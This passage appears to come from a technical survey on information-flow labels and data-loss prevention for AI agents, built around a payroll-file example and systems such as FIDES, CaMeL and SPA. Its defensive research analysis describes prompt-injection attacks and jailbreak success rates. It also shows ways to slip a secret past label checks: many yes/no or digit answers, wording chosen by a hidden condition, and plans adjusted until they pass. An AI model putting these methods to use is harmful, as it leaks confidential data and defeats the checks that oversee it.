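Microsoft plans to close the gap, but the feature was still in development in July 2026, despite the title of its entry, *Endpoint DLP now detects sensitivity labels on files inside archives* (2026). That month, Microsoft postponed the preview from July to December 2026 and the general release from August 2026 to January 2027, according to its version history. A company should test the feature on its own computers before relying on it.

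#### After conversion or a Copilot summary

Converting a file can remove its label. According to Microsoft's *Known issues for the information protection client*, saving a labelled .docx, .xlsx or .pptx file in an Office 97–2003 format removes the label. Exporting payroll.xlsx to CSV would also remove an embedded label, because CSV has no place to store it. Under Tether's rules, either conversion counts as a copy, so the new file would keep the payroll label.

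Purview includes a data-loss-prevention policy for Copilot, Microsoft's AI assistant. Office 365 for IT Pros' *Primer* reports that Microsoft has extended this policy to Office files in any storage location, including those outside SharePoint and OneDrive. The policy limits Copilot's use of the source file, but that doesn't mean a permitted summary of payroll.xlsx inherits the file's label. A company should therefore check the summary's label before letting anyone send it out.

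### Reading the contents of archives

If a label-based rule misses payroll.zip, a content filter may still recognise the salaries. Microsoft's *Archive File Support for Mac Endpoints* (2024) describes the usual method, in which the software opens the archive, scans every file in a supported format and applies the resulting restriction to the whole archive. This resembles a join, except that the filter infers sensitivity from text, so it must be able to read each file.

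Data loss prevention (DLP) tools from Microsoft and Check Point support most common archive formats. Microsoft's *Learn about Endpoint data loss prevention* lists .zip, .zipx, .rar, .7z, .tar and .gz among the files that Endpoint DLP can scan. Microsoft's *Enhanced content extraction and file type coverage for DLP on Windows devices* adds bzip2 files in an expansion from 40 file types to more than 100. Check Point's *Data Loss Prevention Policies* lists similar formats, including .jar files and self-extracting zip archives.

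Support can differ by operating system. Microsoft announced archive scanning for Macs in 2024, but its Endpoint DLP documentation lists archives as monitored files only on Windows. On Windows, Endpoint DLP used to skip certain folders, including temporary ones, where an agent might well put an archive before sending it. In 2026, Microsoft let administrators cover files in those folders when someone tries to upload or copy them elsewhere.

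A scanner may check only part of a large archive. Palo Alto Networks limits the total size of an archive, and if a scan runs out of time, its software applies the rules to whatever it has read. If payroll.csv comes after several large videos in an archive, the scan might never reach it.

Password-protected archives are harder to handle because software can't read their contents without the password. Hesham (2024) reported in *DLP Policy Not Scanning Inside Compressed Files (Purview)*, a Microsoft forum post, that such archives got past his Purview rules. He wanted to block only those that contained sensitive data. This is one administrator's account of one configuration, but a content filter generally can't tell which password-protected archives contain sensitive data. Tether could, because it would have labelled the archive when the agent created it.

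Renaming a file can also affect whether these products record activity on it. Endpoint DLP continues to record activity on Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF files under any new extension. For some other types, including .txt and .tsv, it does so only if the new extension is also supported. Neither list includes .csv or .zip, so Microsoft's documentation doesn't show whether recording continues after the agent renames payroll.csv to payroll.dat.

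Endpoint DLP uses both approaches for the clipboard. It can block someone from copying text out of a sensitive Word document because of where the text came from, even if the selected sentence is harmless. When someone pastes text into a website, it checks only the pasted text, not the source file's classification.

### Vendor claims about agents

Independent evidence on how often commercial products stop leaks is scarce. IT Brew's *Is data leak prevention built for AI?* reports on a survey of more than 433 IT professionals by the Cloud Security Alliance, an industry non-profit. Only 16% of reported detections had been blocked before the data left. The alliance ran the survey with Jazz, which sells a competing kind of data-loss-prevention product and benefits if older ones look weak. The percentage also excludes leaks that nobody detected, and some companies set their software to record transfers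 without blocking them.

Some vendors now advertise tracking that resembles taint tracking. Help Net Security's *Cyberhaven launches Agentic Data Security to track and control AI data use* describes a product that uses data lineage, a record of where data came from and how it moved, to monitor AI agents and stop sensitive data from leaving. With lineage, the product could in principle connect payroll.zip to payroll.csv without reading either file. But the announcement includes no test results and does not explain what happens to the lineage when an agent compresses a file, loads it into a database or rewrites it in its own words.

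## Keeping labels when a language model handles the data

When an agent rewrites a file in its own words, the new text may have no bytes in common with the old. For example, if payroll.csv gives Ben's salary as "150000", the agent can write "a hundred and fifty thousand" in an email to Carol. Decoding Base64 doesn't help a filter catch this, because the text isn't encoded.

Tracking labels through the model's machine instructions doesn't solve the problem. A language model splits text into tokens, which are words or pieces of words. It looks up each token in a table to get a list of numbers, repeatedly mixes the numbers for different tokens, and picks the next token by comparing scores. A tracker that ignores lookups and comparisons would lose the payroll label, as it does in gzip, but one that follows them would mark every word of the reply with the labels of everything the model has read,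 because any token in the input may influence any token in the output.

### The context label

Careful tracking would mark everything anyway, so a tracker can treat the model as a single unit and give everything it writes the context label. This label joins the labels on everything the model has been shown in the session. If payroll.csv is in the context, a paraphrase, a translation and a one-word answer all get the payroll label.

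The box rule costs little when the agent sends a whole archive, but a model's reply may depend on one line of its context and on nothing else. The rule gives the reply every label anyway. Suppose Ana asks her agent to work through her inbox:

| Step | Who may read the new text | Context label afterwards | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read Ana's request | Anyone | Anyone | |
| Read a public notice of the office's opening hours | Anyone | Anyone | |
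| Read Ben's email about his salary | {Ana, Ben} | {Ana, Ben} | |
| Send Carol the opening hours | | {Ana, Ben} | Refused |
| Read Dana's email about her holiday | {Ana, Dana} | {Ana} | |
| Tell Ben "See you at noon" | | {Ana} | Refused |

The opening hours are public, but the model wrote the message to Carol after reading Ben's email, so only Ana and Ben may receive it. After the model reads Dana's email, the agent can't answer Ben either. It can write only to Ana for the rest of the session, because joins never add readers. Deleting the two emails from the context wouldn't be enough to lower the label, because anything the model wrote after reading them may repeat their contents. The agent could have sent Carol the opening hours before opening Ben's email, or in a new session.

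### Hiding results in variables

FIDES, the system by Costa and colleagues, slows this growth by keeping labelled text out of the context. Its planner is the part that maintains the conversation and asks the model what to do next. A tracking loop around the planner runs the tools and checks the labels:

1. The planner sends the conversation to the model, and the loop gives the reply the context label.
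2. If the reply requests a tool call, the loop checks the labels on the request and on each argument against the company's policy, such as the export rule. If the check fails, the tool doesn't run.
3. If the check passes, the loop runs the tool. The result gets the join of the labels on the request, the arguments and any stored data the tool may have read. Anything the tool may have written gets the same label.
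4. The planner compares the result's label with the context label. If adding the result would make the context label stricter, the planner stores the result in a variable and adds only the variable's name to the conversation.
5. The model can use that name as an argument in a later call. The planner then substitutes the stored contents, with their original label, before the loop makes its check.

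A basic planner has no step 4 and adds every result to the conversation, which is why the context label in Ana's inbox grew so quickly. FIDES applies step 4 to each field of a result separately, so the model may see an email's date while the body stays in a variable.

Passing data by reference in this way changes what else the agent can do in the payroll example:

| Action | Planner sees the file | File stays in a variable |
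|---|---|---|
| Read payroll.csv | The salaries enter the context, whose label becomes {Ana, Ben} | The name `#read_file_0` enters the context, whose label stays public |
| Compress it | The archive gets {Ana, Ben} | The compressor receives the contents of `#read_file_0`; the archive gets {Ana, Ben} and becomes `#compress_0` |
| Email the archive to Ben | Allowed | Allowed |
| Email the archive to Carol | Refused | Refused |
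| Email Carol the opening hours | Refused | Allowed |

The archive has the same label in both runs, so the export rule protects the salaries equally well. Only the last row differs. In the second run the model never receives a salary, so it can't put one into the message about opening hours.

Under step 3, even a short message from the compressor, such as "done", gets the payroll label and goes into a variable. The company could label the message field as public so that the planner can handle errors. This would reveal to the planner whether compression succeeded, which seems harmless for most files.

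### Questions to an isolated model

Variables are enough if the agent only has to move the file, but a model has to read the file to summarise it. In 2023 the programmer Simon Willison proposed the Dual LLM pattern, which divides the work between two models. One plans and calls tools but never sees risky text. The other reads the text but has no tools, so an instruction hidden in the text can't make it send anything.

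FIDES gives the planner the isolated model as a tool named `query_llm`. The planner passes it a question and one or more variables, and the answer goes into a new variable. That variable's label is the join of the context label and the labels on all the variables in the query. If the agent asks for a summary of `#read_file_0`, the summary gets the label {Ana, Ben}, even if it doesn't repeat any figures from the file. The planner can then email the summary to Ben without reading it.

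The isolated model can still make mistakes or be misled. Costa and colleagues give the example of an email that contains an instruction to produce an empty summary. An attacker can spoil the answer this way but can't choose who receives it.

If the planner needs the contents to decide what to do next, it can call another tool, `inspect`, which puts them into the conversation and raises the context label.

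### Labels that include the type of answer

Sometimes the planner needs only a small fact, such as whether payroll.csv has an entry for every employee. FIDES lets it request an answer of a fixed type, in this case "true" or "false". Constrained decoding ensures the answer has that type by stopping the model from producing any token that doesn't fit the required format.

Costa and colleagues make the type part of the label. They order types by how much information a value can carry:

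bool ⊑ enum["a", "b", "c"] ⊑ string

The answer about missing entries gets the label ({Ana, Ben}, bool), while a free-text answer gets ({Ana, Ben}, string). A policy can treat the two differently. For example, it could let the agent act on a yes-or-no answer from the payroll file even when outsiders can see the action, because the answer reveals at most one bit.

Costa and colleagues use this mainly to stop prompt injection. The case for that use is strong, because an attacker who controls only one bit of the planner's context can't write an instruction there. Secrecy is harder to protect, because a single bit may contain all the information Carol wants.

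The bits also add up, and the label doesn't record the total. Types combine by a join, and the join of bool and bool is bool. After a thousand yes-or-no answers, the type in the context label is still bool. In general, k answers with n possible values each can reveal up to

k × log₂ n bits

A salary below a million dollars takes about 20 bits, so an agent that asks well-chosen questions about one salary at a time needs this many answers:

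| Type of answer | Bits per answer | Answers for one salary | Answers for 500 salaries |
|---|---|---|---|
| Yes or no | 1 | 20 | 10,000 |
| One decimal digit | 3.32 | 6 | 3,000 |
| One of 256 options | 8 | 3 | 1,500 |

An agent could ask for Ben's salary in six queries, one digit at a time, and each answer would look like only a small choice. The running total that any bit limit requires must therefore include these answers. Costa and colleagues note that their loop could check policies against the whole history of labelled actions, so the loop is a natural place to keep the total. The total would have to carry over between sessions, or the agent could start a new session whenever it reached the limit.

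### CaMeL and plans written in advance

In FIDES, the model chooses each action after seeing what came before. CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind and elsewhere published in 2025, has the model write the whole plan before the agent reads any data. As Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, explain, the planning model sees only the user's request and expresses the plan in a restricted form of Python. For Ana, it might write:

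```
salaries = read_file("payroll.csv")
summary = ask_isolated_model("Summarise the changes since May", salaries)
send_email("Ben", summary)
```

An interpreter runs the program and attaches two tags to each value. *Sources* records where the value came from, and *Readers* records who may read it. Here `summary` inherits the tags on `salaries`. Before each tool call, a policy written as a Python function checks the call, its arguments and their tags, then allows or denies the call. If the program sent `summary` to Carol, the policy could deny the call because Carol isn't among the readers.

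The planning model never reads payroll.csv, so CaMeL has no context label that grows during the task. Carol's invoice can't add a step to the program either. But Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) point out in *Can CaMeLs Talk?* that the data can still influence which of the program's existing branches run. They also found that provenance can get lost when one agent passes data to another inside an instruction, so a system of several agents has to send the labels along with the data.

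A written plan also provides code that a checker can examine before anything runs, which agents otherwise lack. Nikolaou and colleagues convert the plan into a finite set of states and use a model checker, a program that searches all possible paths, to look for violations. If the checker finds one, it sends the planning model a description of the path that led to it, and the model can then repair the plan.

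The reliability of such checks depends partly on the programming language. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) argues that even a restricted form of Python is a poor choice. An error partway through a Python program can change which code runs next, and the type of a value may be unknown until the program runs. Both make it difficult to give firm guarantees about information flow. The paper recommends a dedicated language with bounded loops and simple conditions.

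### SPA and the label on decisions

SPA (Girrens and Wang, 2026) uses a language of roughly this kind. A plan can contain only six kinds of step: retrieve a stored result, call a tool, query an isolated model, show something to the user, branch, and loop. SPA checks the labels throughout the plan before running any of it.

Its main addition is a label for the control context, written pc, which records what the decision to run a step depended on. For a step that uses the values x₁, …, xₙ, SPA computes

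L(step) = pc ⊔ L(x₁) ⊔ … ⊔ L(xₙ)

and compares the result with the most sensitive data that the tool may receive. Inside a branch, pc also includes the label on the condition. Inside a loop, it includes the label on the list that the loop goes through.

FIDES's checks on arguments miss the leak when an agent refreshes a public web page only if Ben earns more than 100,000. Under SPA, the condition has the payroll label, so pc has it too, and so does the refresh. SPA checks both branches without running either, so it rejects the plan whatever Ben earns, and Carol can't learn anything from the rejection. SPA thus prevents this kind of implicit flow, which explicit secrecy permits.

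One smaller leak seems to remain. SPA stops a plan when a step fails, but a step that might fail doesn't raise pc for the steps after it. If a salary in an unexpected format makes one step fail, a public message later in the plan won't go out, and Carol can learn something about the file from the missing message.

SPA also gives each tool a single fixed clearance so, as described, it can't distinguish Ben from Carol when both receive mail through the same tool. Ana's company would need one email tool for the payroll group and another for everyone else. CaMeL's policies and FIDES's export rule can check the actual recipients.

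#### Labels that last until the next request

A persistent agent can also lose a label between tasks. On Monday, Ana has her agent compress payroll.csv for Ben. On Tuesday, having forgotten what was in the archive, she asks the agent to send "yesterday's archive" to an outside printer. If the agent has kept the archive but not its label, it sends the salaries to the printer.

SPA stores each result in three parts: the contents, the label and a description. The planner sees only the description, which includes the result's format and two notes, one on why the agent produced it and one on what it contains. The planner wrote both notes before any tool ran, so they can't contain salaries. On Tuesday, the planner can use the description to pick the right archive and plan to email it. The retrieve step brings back the label along with the contents, and SPA rejects the plan.

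SPA rejects a plan without giving a reason or allowing another attempt, because Girrens and Wang want to prevent the planner from adjusting an unsafe plan until one version passes. Nikolaou and colleagues instead return the offending path for repair. This feedback helps a planner that is pursuing the user's task to finish it, but it would also help a planner with other goals to search for gaps in the policy.

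### Test results

Most of the evidence comes from AgentDojo, a benchmark that simulates office work, travel booking, banking and the chat program Slack. It has 97 ordinary tasks and a set of attacks that hide instructions in the data the agent reads.

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES in 2025 with GPT-4o and o1, both much older than today's models. With GPT-4o, 152 attacks succeeded against a plain agent, 21 against FIDES with its policy checks off, and none against FIDES with the checks on. No attacks succeeded against the basic planner with checks either, so the checks provided the security. The variables helped agents finish their tasks despite the checks. FIDES completed 8 percentage points more tasks than the basic planner with GPT-4o, and 16 points more with o1.

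In *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) reran FIDES on newer models and built Prudentia on top of it. FIDES's planner isn't given the policies, so it sometimes opens a variable unnecessarily and then can't finish the task. Prudentia gives the planner the labels and policies, and requires it to provide a justification before opening a variable.

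| System | Model | Tasks completed with label checks and no human approval | Comparison |
|---|---|---|---|
| FIDES, in Costa and colleagues | GPT-4o | 50% | 84% for a plain agent without checks |
| FIDES, in Costa and colleagues | o1 | 61% | 84% for a plain agent without checks |
| FIDES, in Kolluri and colleagues | GPT-5 | 57% | 72% for a plain agent with unlimited human approval |
| Prudentia, in Kolluri and colleagues | GPT-5 | 73% | 72% for a plain agent with unlimited human approval |
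| SPA, in Girrens and Wang | gpt-5.4-nano | 29% | 53% for SPA without label checks |

The first two rows are simple averages over the four environments. The systems can't be ranked from these rows because the models, policies and scoring differ. Still, Prudentia's result suggests that much of the lost work under FIDES came from poor planning rather than from the label rules. But Prudentia needs a capable model. With GPT-4o, it completed 42.5% of tasks unaided, compared with 50.3% for FIDES. It also uses more model time than FIDES because it adds planning steps to the extra queries that FIDES already makes.

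*Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) reports that CaMeL stopped nearly all AgentDojo attacks with comparable task performance. Kolluri and colleagues, however, put the loss from defences such as FIDES and CaMeL at up to 30% of task completion. Both results are from older models. In October 2026, Peters-Gill and colleagues tested CaMeL with five models on a multi-agent version of AgentDojo. Attacks succeeded in 12.9% of runs without CaMeL and 0.2% with it. They configured no data policies, so this measures only the protection from CaMeL's fixed plan.

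SPA blocked all 949 attack runs on AgentDojo. Without label checks, attacks succeeded in only 0.4% of runs, so writing the plan first already stopped nearly all of them. Girrens and Wang also tested a version that split each task into several requests, where the checks lowered the attack success rate from 0.3% to 0.2%. The remaining 0.2% is about two runs, and they identify two that the benchmark counted as successful attacks even though SPA had rejected the plan. Task completion fell from 62.5% to 35.3%. They acknowledge that the benchmark barely tests attacks whose instructions lie dormant between requests.

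#### What the tests say about leaks

These experiments are much better evidence about hijacked agents than about leaked files. Costa and colleagues created variables only for untrusted data, not for data that was merely confidential, and they left out constrained decoding. The second run in the payroll example and the one-bit answers therefore follow from their design, but the experiments did not test them.

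Their policy for sending email was also looser than the export rule. It allowed a message if either every recipient could read the data or the planner had chosen the call in a trusted context. Kolluri and colleagues used the same either-or rule. Under that rule, an agent that kept payroll.csv in a variable could send the archive to Carol by mistake. For payroll data, Ana's company should always require that every recipient can read the data, though agents might complete fewer tasks under this stricter rule.

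SPA's low score, however, may exaggerate how much protecting secrets hurts performance. SPA rejected about 53% of runs on the original benchmark, typically because the plan passed untrusted data to a tool that required trusted input. Girrens and Wang didn't test sensitivity labels separately. gpt-5.4-nano is also a small model, and some plans failed before any label check.

### Tasks that require the planner to see the data

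Costa and colleagues separate tasks by whether the same actions work whatever the data says. Let A(t, d) be the set of action sequences that complete task t when the stored data is d. The task is data independent if at least one sequence works for every possible d:

⋂ A(t, d) ≠ ∅, taken over all d

"Compress payroll.csv and send it to Ben" meets this condition, since the steps don't change with the salaries. Other requests about the same file need more:

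| Task | What the planner has to learn |
|---|---|
| Compress payroll.csv and send it to Ben | Nothing |
| Send Ben a summary of payroll.csv | Nothing, because the isolated model writes it |
| Ask Ben for an update if any salary is missing | One bit |
| Handle an email as a meeting request, an invoice or a complaint | One choice out of three |
| Make the corrections described in a note at the end of the file | The note |
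| Find out why the payroll import fails, and fix it | Error messages and data, probably several times |

CaMeL and SPA can handle the two middle cases with a branch in the plan, so their planners don't need to receive even the one bit. The last two cases are different because nobody can list the possible actions in advance. The note might contain a request for a changed salary, a deleted row or an email to Dana, and the cause of the import failure may become clear only after the agent has tried something.

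Costa and colleagues classify about a fifth of AgentDojo's tasks as data dependent. The share is 5% in the office environment but more than 40% in banking and Slack, where many tasks tell the agent to read a file or web page and follow its instructions. Some data-dependent tasks need only a yes-or-no answer, so a smaller share requires the full text.

FIDES can attempt the open-ended tasks by opening the variable, which makes the context label stricter. CaMeL and SPA keep the plan fixed, so Ana would have to read the note herself and turn it into a new request.

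Opening the file does not always block the task. If the agent corrects payroll.csv and reports only to Ana and Ben, the label {Ana, Ben} permits every message it has to send. The label conflicts with a task when the planner must read the salaries and then write to someone outside that group. This happens when an agent has to diagnose a payroll error and then describe it to the software's outside support desk, even if its description contains no salaries.

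## Estimating which inputs shaped a model's output

An agent has to read payroll.csv to diagnose a payroll error, but sometimes the file is in the context only because of an earlier task. Suppose Ana's agent answers a question from Ben about the file, and Ana then asks it to summarise a public web page for Carol. The context label is {Ana, Ben}, so the export rule stops the agent from sending Carol the summary, even if nothing in it came from the file. Several research groups have built systems to relax the label in such cases. The systems estimate which inputs mattered to the output and drop the labels of the others, so that the summary stays public.

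An input can be unimportant to a model's answer in several senses. The model may be able to write an equally good answer without the input. Changing the input slightly may barely change the answer. Or a second model, given the conversation, may classify the input as unused in the answer.

An input may have shaped an output in one of these senses but not another. If payroll.csv and a public notice both give the office's opening hours, the model can tell Carol the hours from the notice alone, but it may have copied them from the file. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), a survey of ways to record what agents do, similarly distinguishes evidence that supports a conclusion from events that influence it. For example, a false note in an agent's memory can cause an action without supporting anything. Secrecy depends on influence, because Carol can learn about the salaries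 from anything they changed in the text she receives.

### Finding a smaller set of documents

Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2024), in *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, test whether the model needed the documents with the strictest labels. Their method, permissive propagation, has four steps:

1. The model writes an answer from all the documents in its context.
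2. The system looks for a more permissive label. For each candidate, it removes the documents that the label doesn't cover and measures how likely the model would have been to write the same answer from the rest.
3. The system picks a label that passed, and the model writes a new answer from only the documents which that label covers.
4. The system returns the new answer with the new label and discards the original.

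The measure in step 2 is perplexity, which is 1 if the model was certain of every token and rises as the text becomes more surprising to it. For a request x, documents C and an answer y of n tokens,

PPL(C) = [p(y₁ | x, C) × p(y₂ | x, C, y₁) × … × p(yₙ | x, C, y₁ … yₙ₋₁)]^(−1/n)

A candidate label passes if removing the documents raises the perplexity by no more than a chosen tolerance, λ. If the summary for Carol has a perplexity of 1.3 with payroll.csv in the context and 1.35 without it, the increase is 0.05, so the summary can be public at λ = 0.2, the value used in one of the experiments.

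With two labels, the search needs a single trial. If n documents all have different reader lists, there can be up to 2ⁿ combinations, so the search skips everything below a candidate that fails. This shortcut is reliable only if extra documents never make an answer worse. That isn't always true, so the search can miss a usable label.

Siddiqui and colleagues used Llama 2 models with 7 and 70 billion parameters, which are far weaker than current models. One test had 64 questions about the identity numbers and birth dates of invented people. Each question came with 14 documents, which gave 2¹⁴ = 16,384 possible labels. The search found exactly the right set of labels for 86% of the questions. When asked which documents it had used, the smaller model gave the right set for 2% of the questions and the larger one for 13%.

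Two other tests used just two labels, trusted and untrusted:

| Test | Model size | Labels correctly relaxed, where possible | Relaxed labels that left out a needed source |
|---|---|---|---|
| News articles | 7 billion | 57% | 23% |
| News articles | 70 billion | 39% | 19% |
| Agent conversations | 7 billion | 85% | 6% |
| Agent conversations | 70 billion | 95% | 10% |

The news figures apply only if the system retrieves every relevant article. With a realistic search tool, the figures in the last column rose to 30% and 26%. The agent test had only 40 conversations, and in half of them the label couldn't be relaxed. Both tests used integrity labels, so they are indirect evidence about keeping salaries secret, although the search handles integrity and confidentiality labels in the same way.

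### Why the model writes the answer again

The errors in the last column would put secrets at risk if the system kept the original answer and changed only its label. In the news test, roughly one relaxed label in five would have been wrong.

Perplexity has a particular weakness here because it averages over the whole text. Suppose a 200-token summary includes Ben's exact salary, which the model could guess without the file only one time in a million. If nothing else in the summary depends on the file, removing the file multiplies the perplexity by

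(10⁶)^(1/200) ≈ 1.07

Perplexity rises from 1.3 to 1.39, and the increase of 0.09 is within λ = 0.2. The search would therefore approve a public label for a summary that states Ben's salary. In a 20-token reply, the same salary would double the perplexity, and the search would reject the public label.

Regenerating the answer without the payroll data removes this risk. Let P be the public page, D the payroll data and M the model. Relabelling would send Carol the original answer, M(x, P, D), but Siddiqui and colleagues' system sends her M(x, P). The new answer can't reveal the salaries because they aren't among its inputs. This holds even if an attacker misleads the search, because the system, not the model, removes the payroll data.

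A wrong estimate therefore lowers the quality of the answer rather than exposing secret data. In the agent test, Siddiqui and colleagues scored the new answers from 0 to 1 by their overlap with reference answers. The score hardly changed when the omitted source was unnecessary, but fell by about 0.3 when the answer needed it.

The guarantee covers only what the system leaves out. Ana's request must not contain payroll data, and anything the model wrote after reading the file must keep the payroll label so that the system removes it too.

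The choice of label can also leak a little information, because the system has access to every document when it chooses. Suppose the web page contains an instruction to quote Ben's salary if he earns more than 100,000. If he earns less, the search drops the payroll.csv label because the file is unnecessary, and Carol receives a public summary. If he earns more, the search may keep the label, and the export rule then blocks the email. Carol can learn one bit about Ben's salary from whether the summary arrives.

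This leak is avoidable when the recipient, here Carol, is known in advance. Siddiqui and colleagues note that if the required label is known beforehand, the system can skip the search and give the model only documents that the label covers. They relate their approach to secure multi-execution, an older technique that runs a program once for each security level and gives each run only the data permitted at that level. The search is more useful for text whose future readers are not yet known, such as an email that Ben may later forward.

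### Measuring influence with small changes

Geometric Information Flow (GIF), by Storek, Holzer and colleagues (2026), measures influence inside the model. For a stretch of the input, such as the text of payroll.csv, GIF estimates how many bits of mutual information the output would share with a little random noise added to the numbers that represent that stretch's tokens.

Nobody can compute this exactly for a large model. *GIF* (2026), the paper on the method, approximates the model near the actual text by a Gaussian channel, which scales its input and adds bell-curve noise of its own. In one dimension, with input noise U of variance σ², channel noise N of variance τ² and a scaling factor j,

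Y = jU + N

I(U; Y) = ½ log₂(1 + j²σ²/τ²)

If j is zero, the output reveals nothing about U. If j²σ²/τ² is 3, it reveals one bit. In a real model, j becomes the Jacobian, the table of how much each output number changes when each input number changes slightly. GIF estimates the quantities it needs without writing out the whole table, which would be enormous. A machine-checked proof in Lean 4 shows that, under mild assumptions, the score is an upper bound on the local flow.

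The proof covers only local influence, which limits what it establishes about secrets. Suppose the model answers "yes" because Ben's salary of 150,000 is more than 100,000. A slight change to the numbers that represent his salary would leave the answer at "yes", so the measured influence could be close to zero. But a salary of 90,000 would have changed the answer, so Carol learns that Ben earns more than 100,000. A local measure can therefore miss the same kind of implicit flow that ordinary taint trackers miss.

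*Sightline* (2026) builds on GIF and states the same restriction to small changes. It bounds influence using attention weights, which set how much each token draws on earlier ones. Taint spreads from token to token in proportion to these weights, including along indirect routes. If no route connects the payroll text to the output, *Sightline* calculates a local flow of zero. Ordinary attention gives every earlier token a nonzero weight, though, so a flow of zero usually requires the system to cut the routes itself.

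Storek and colleagues report that GIF found nearly all the real flows in tests of prompt injection and privacy leaks. They paired it with a small language model to classify which of the flagged flows were harmless. The combination did at least as well as GPT-5.5 classifying the flows by itself, and used up to 81 times fewer tokens. Scores from small models also carried over to models up to 200 times larger, which could help a company whose provider doesn't expose the model's internals. The proof doesn't carry over, because a bound computed from one model's Jacobian isn't guaranteed to hold for another. GIF also missed some flows, and relabelling the text based on its scores would release them.

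### Screening the context before the model writes

*RTBAS* (Zhong, Chen and colleagues, 2025) filters the conversation before each message or tool call. A screener picks the parts that the next step needs. The system joins the labels on those parts and blanks out everything that the joined label doesn't cover. The model then works from what remains. If its tool call would still break the company's policy, the system asks the user to confirm it.

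For Carol's summary, the screener should pick Ana's request and the web page, and the system would blank out payroll.csv. If the screener wrongly picks the file too, the summary gets the payroll label and Ana has to approve the email. If it leaves out something useful, the summary may be worse. Zhong and colleagues' conclusion that a screener's mistakes can't compromise security holds for the text of the message. However, the screener reads the whole conversation, so its choices can still reveal a little of it through which messages are sent.

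One version of the screener is a language model that judges which parts are relevant. The other feeds attention scores from a small open model to a network that was trained on 40 cases and was right 81% of the time on test data. It needs a draft of the message to analyse, so the agent's model has to run twice.

Zhong and colleagues tried both on 37 tasks in shopping, payments and flight booking:

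| System | Tasks with a needless request for approval | Tasks where it hid private data instead of asking |
|---|---|---|
| Hide all private data | 0 | 19 |
| Ask before every tool call | 11 | 0 |
| RTBAS with a model as judge | 3 | 4 |
| RTBAS with attention scores | 6 | 4 |

Hiding data by mistake doesn't leak it, but it can stop an agent from completing a task, such as booking a flight that requires a card number. The attention version was also poor at identifying exactly which kinds of private data a call involved. It was right for 57.3% of calls, compared with 56.7% for a system that assumed every call used all the private data and 70% for the judge.

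On AgentDojo, with GPT-4o as the agent, RTBAS stopped every attack that broke its policy. In one case, the possible injection was in text the user had written, which RTBAS didn't track because it had a trusted label. Without attacks, agents completed about 10% fewer tasks with the judge and 7% fewer with attention scores. On the banking tasks, the judge roughly doubled the running time and the price.

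### Confidence scores and labels chosen by a model

*Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, 2026) describes NeuroTaint, which examines the record of an agent's run after the run finishes and gives each suspected flow a confidence score between 0 and 1. It first checks the outgoing call for the source's content, looking for overlapping text, similar meaning and a unique marker that NeuroTaint added to the source.

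If NeuroTaint finds nothing, it looks for a causal contribution. It replaces the source with a neutral placeholder and asks a language model whether the agent would still have made the call. If the model answers no, NeuroTaint reports that the source influenced the agent's decision. It scores the flow using the confidence the model reports, which Cai and colleagues warn against reading as a calibrated probability.

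Like SPA, NeuroTaint saves labels alongside what an agent stores, so it can connect a note in the agent's memory to a report written days later.

Cai and colleagues built a benchmark of 400 scenarios, half of which contained a real flow. NeuroTaint found 187 of the 200 flows and raised 16 false alarms. Ten of the 13 misses involved content the agent had reworded or retrieved in a later session, and the other three involved influence on a decision. Most false alarms came from text on the same topic as the source or from facts the model already knew. The tests didn't include deliberately hidden messages, such as text that uses lookalike characters.

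FIDES found 108 flows on the same benchmark and raised 106 false alarms. The comparison makes FIDES look worse than it should, because Cai and colleagues had it treat any path from source to sink as strong evidence of a flow, which is reasonable for a system meant to prevent leaks. Wang and colleagues advise more caution about findings in this area, where much of the work, including the papers on FIDES and NeuroTaint, had not yet passed peer review.

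*SafeFlow* (Dai, Ying and colleagues, 2026) uses a model to assign the initial labels. It addresses groups of agents in which one reads a file, another rewrites it and a third sends it, so that each step looks harmless. The model chooses from a fixed list of seven labels, including one for reading sensitive data and one for sending data outside. Fixed rules then copy the labels from step to step and hold back irreversible actions until the system has checked the whole workflow.

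Dai and colleagues call this conditional determinism. The rules always give the same result for the same records, but the model may produce different records on another run. If the model doesn't mark the reading of payroll.csv as sensitive, the rules have no label to copy. A company that already labels its files can avoid this error by using the file's existing label.

Across four benchmarks, SafeFlow lowered the average attack success rate from 69.3% to 12.7%. The attacks included risky code and other harmful actions as well as leaks. SafeFlow also wrongly blocked between 4.6% and 7.2% of harmless tasks. When attackers wrapped their requests in the most effective of four jailbreaks, which are prompts designed to get around a model's safeguards, 32.3% of attacks succeeded. The rules helped, since letting only three of the seven labels pass between steps raised the success rate without jailbreaks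 to 22.8%. But a system that depends on a model's labels can't be guaranteed to stop every leak, even if its rules are perfect.

### Estimated and guaranteed labels

Costa and colleagues' labels let a system decide deterministically whether a tool call is safe. The system loses that certainty if it lowers the label on existing text based on an estimate. Even a small error rate adds up over repeated leaks. If NeuroTaint had an independent 93.5% chance of catching each leak, it would catch all of ten leaks only about half the time.

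An attacker can make errors more likely by looking for cases that cause them. Carol's instruction could tell the agent to write "nine o'clock" if Ben earns more than 100,000 and "9 am" otherwise. A judge that reads the message would find no salary in it, and both versions are equally good answers. If the system then relabels the message as public, Carol learns whether Ben earns more than 100,000. If the model instead generates the message again without payroll.csv, the wording can't depend on Ben's salary.

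An estimate that makes some errors could prevent more leaks than a strict rule, because people may switch off a rule that blocks most useful work, leaving files such as payroll.zip unprotected. Zhong and colleagues make a similar point about asking users to approve every tool call, since tired users may approve dangerous requests without reading them or abandon the system.

That is a good reason to relax labels, but a weak reason to relabel text the model has already written. If the agent didn't need the file, it can write the message again without it, so keeping the secret doesn't depend on the estimate being right. This takes extra model calls and sometimes gives a worse answer, which seems acceptable when protecting salaries. For less sensitive material, such as an internal canteen menu, a company might reasonably accept an estimated label. Estimates can also help Ana decide which messages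 to read closely before she approves them.

Writing the message again doesn't help when the agent needs the file, as it may to report a payroll error to the outside support desk. Someone then has to decide whether a description based on the file can be sent outside the company.

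## Deciding whether labelled data may go to a recipient

The export rule stops Ana's agent from sending its description of the payroll error to the outside support desk, even if the company wants it sent. To decide whether to make an exception, the system has to identify who would receive the text, and someone or something has to judge whether those people may have the information in it.

### Finding out who will receive the data

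A tool call rarely lists the people who will read the data. It names an address, a channel or a repository, and the system has to work out the rest:

| Outgoing action | What the system looks up | Who counts as a recipient |
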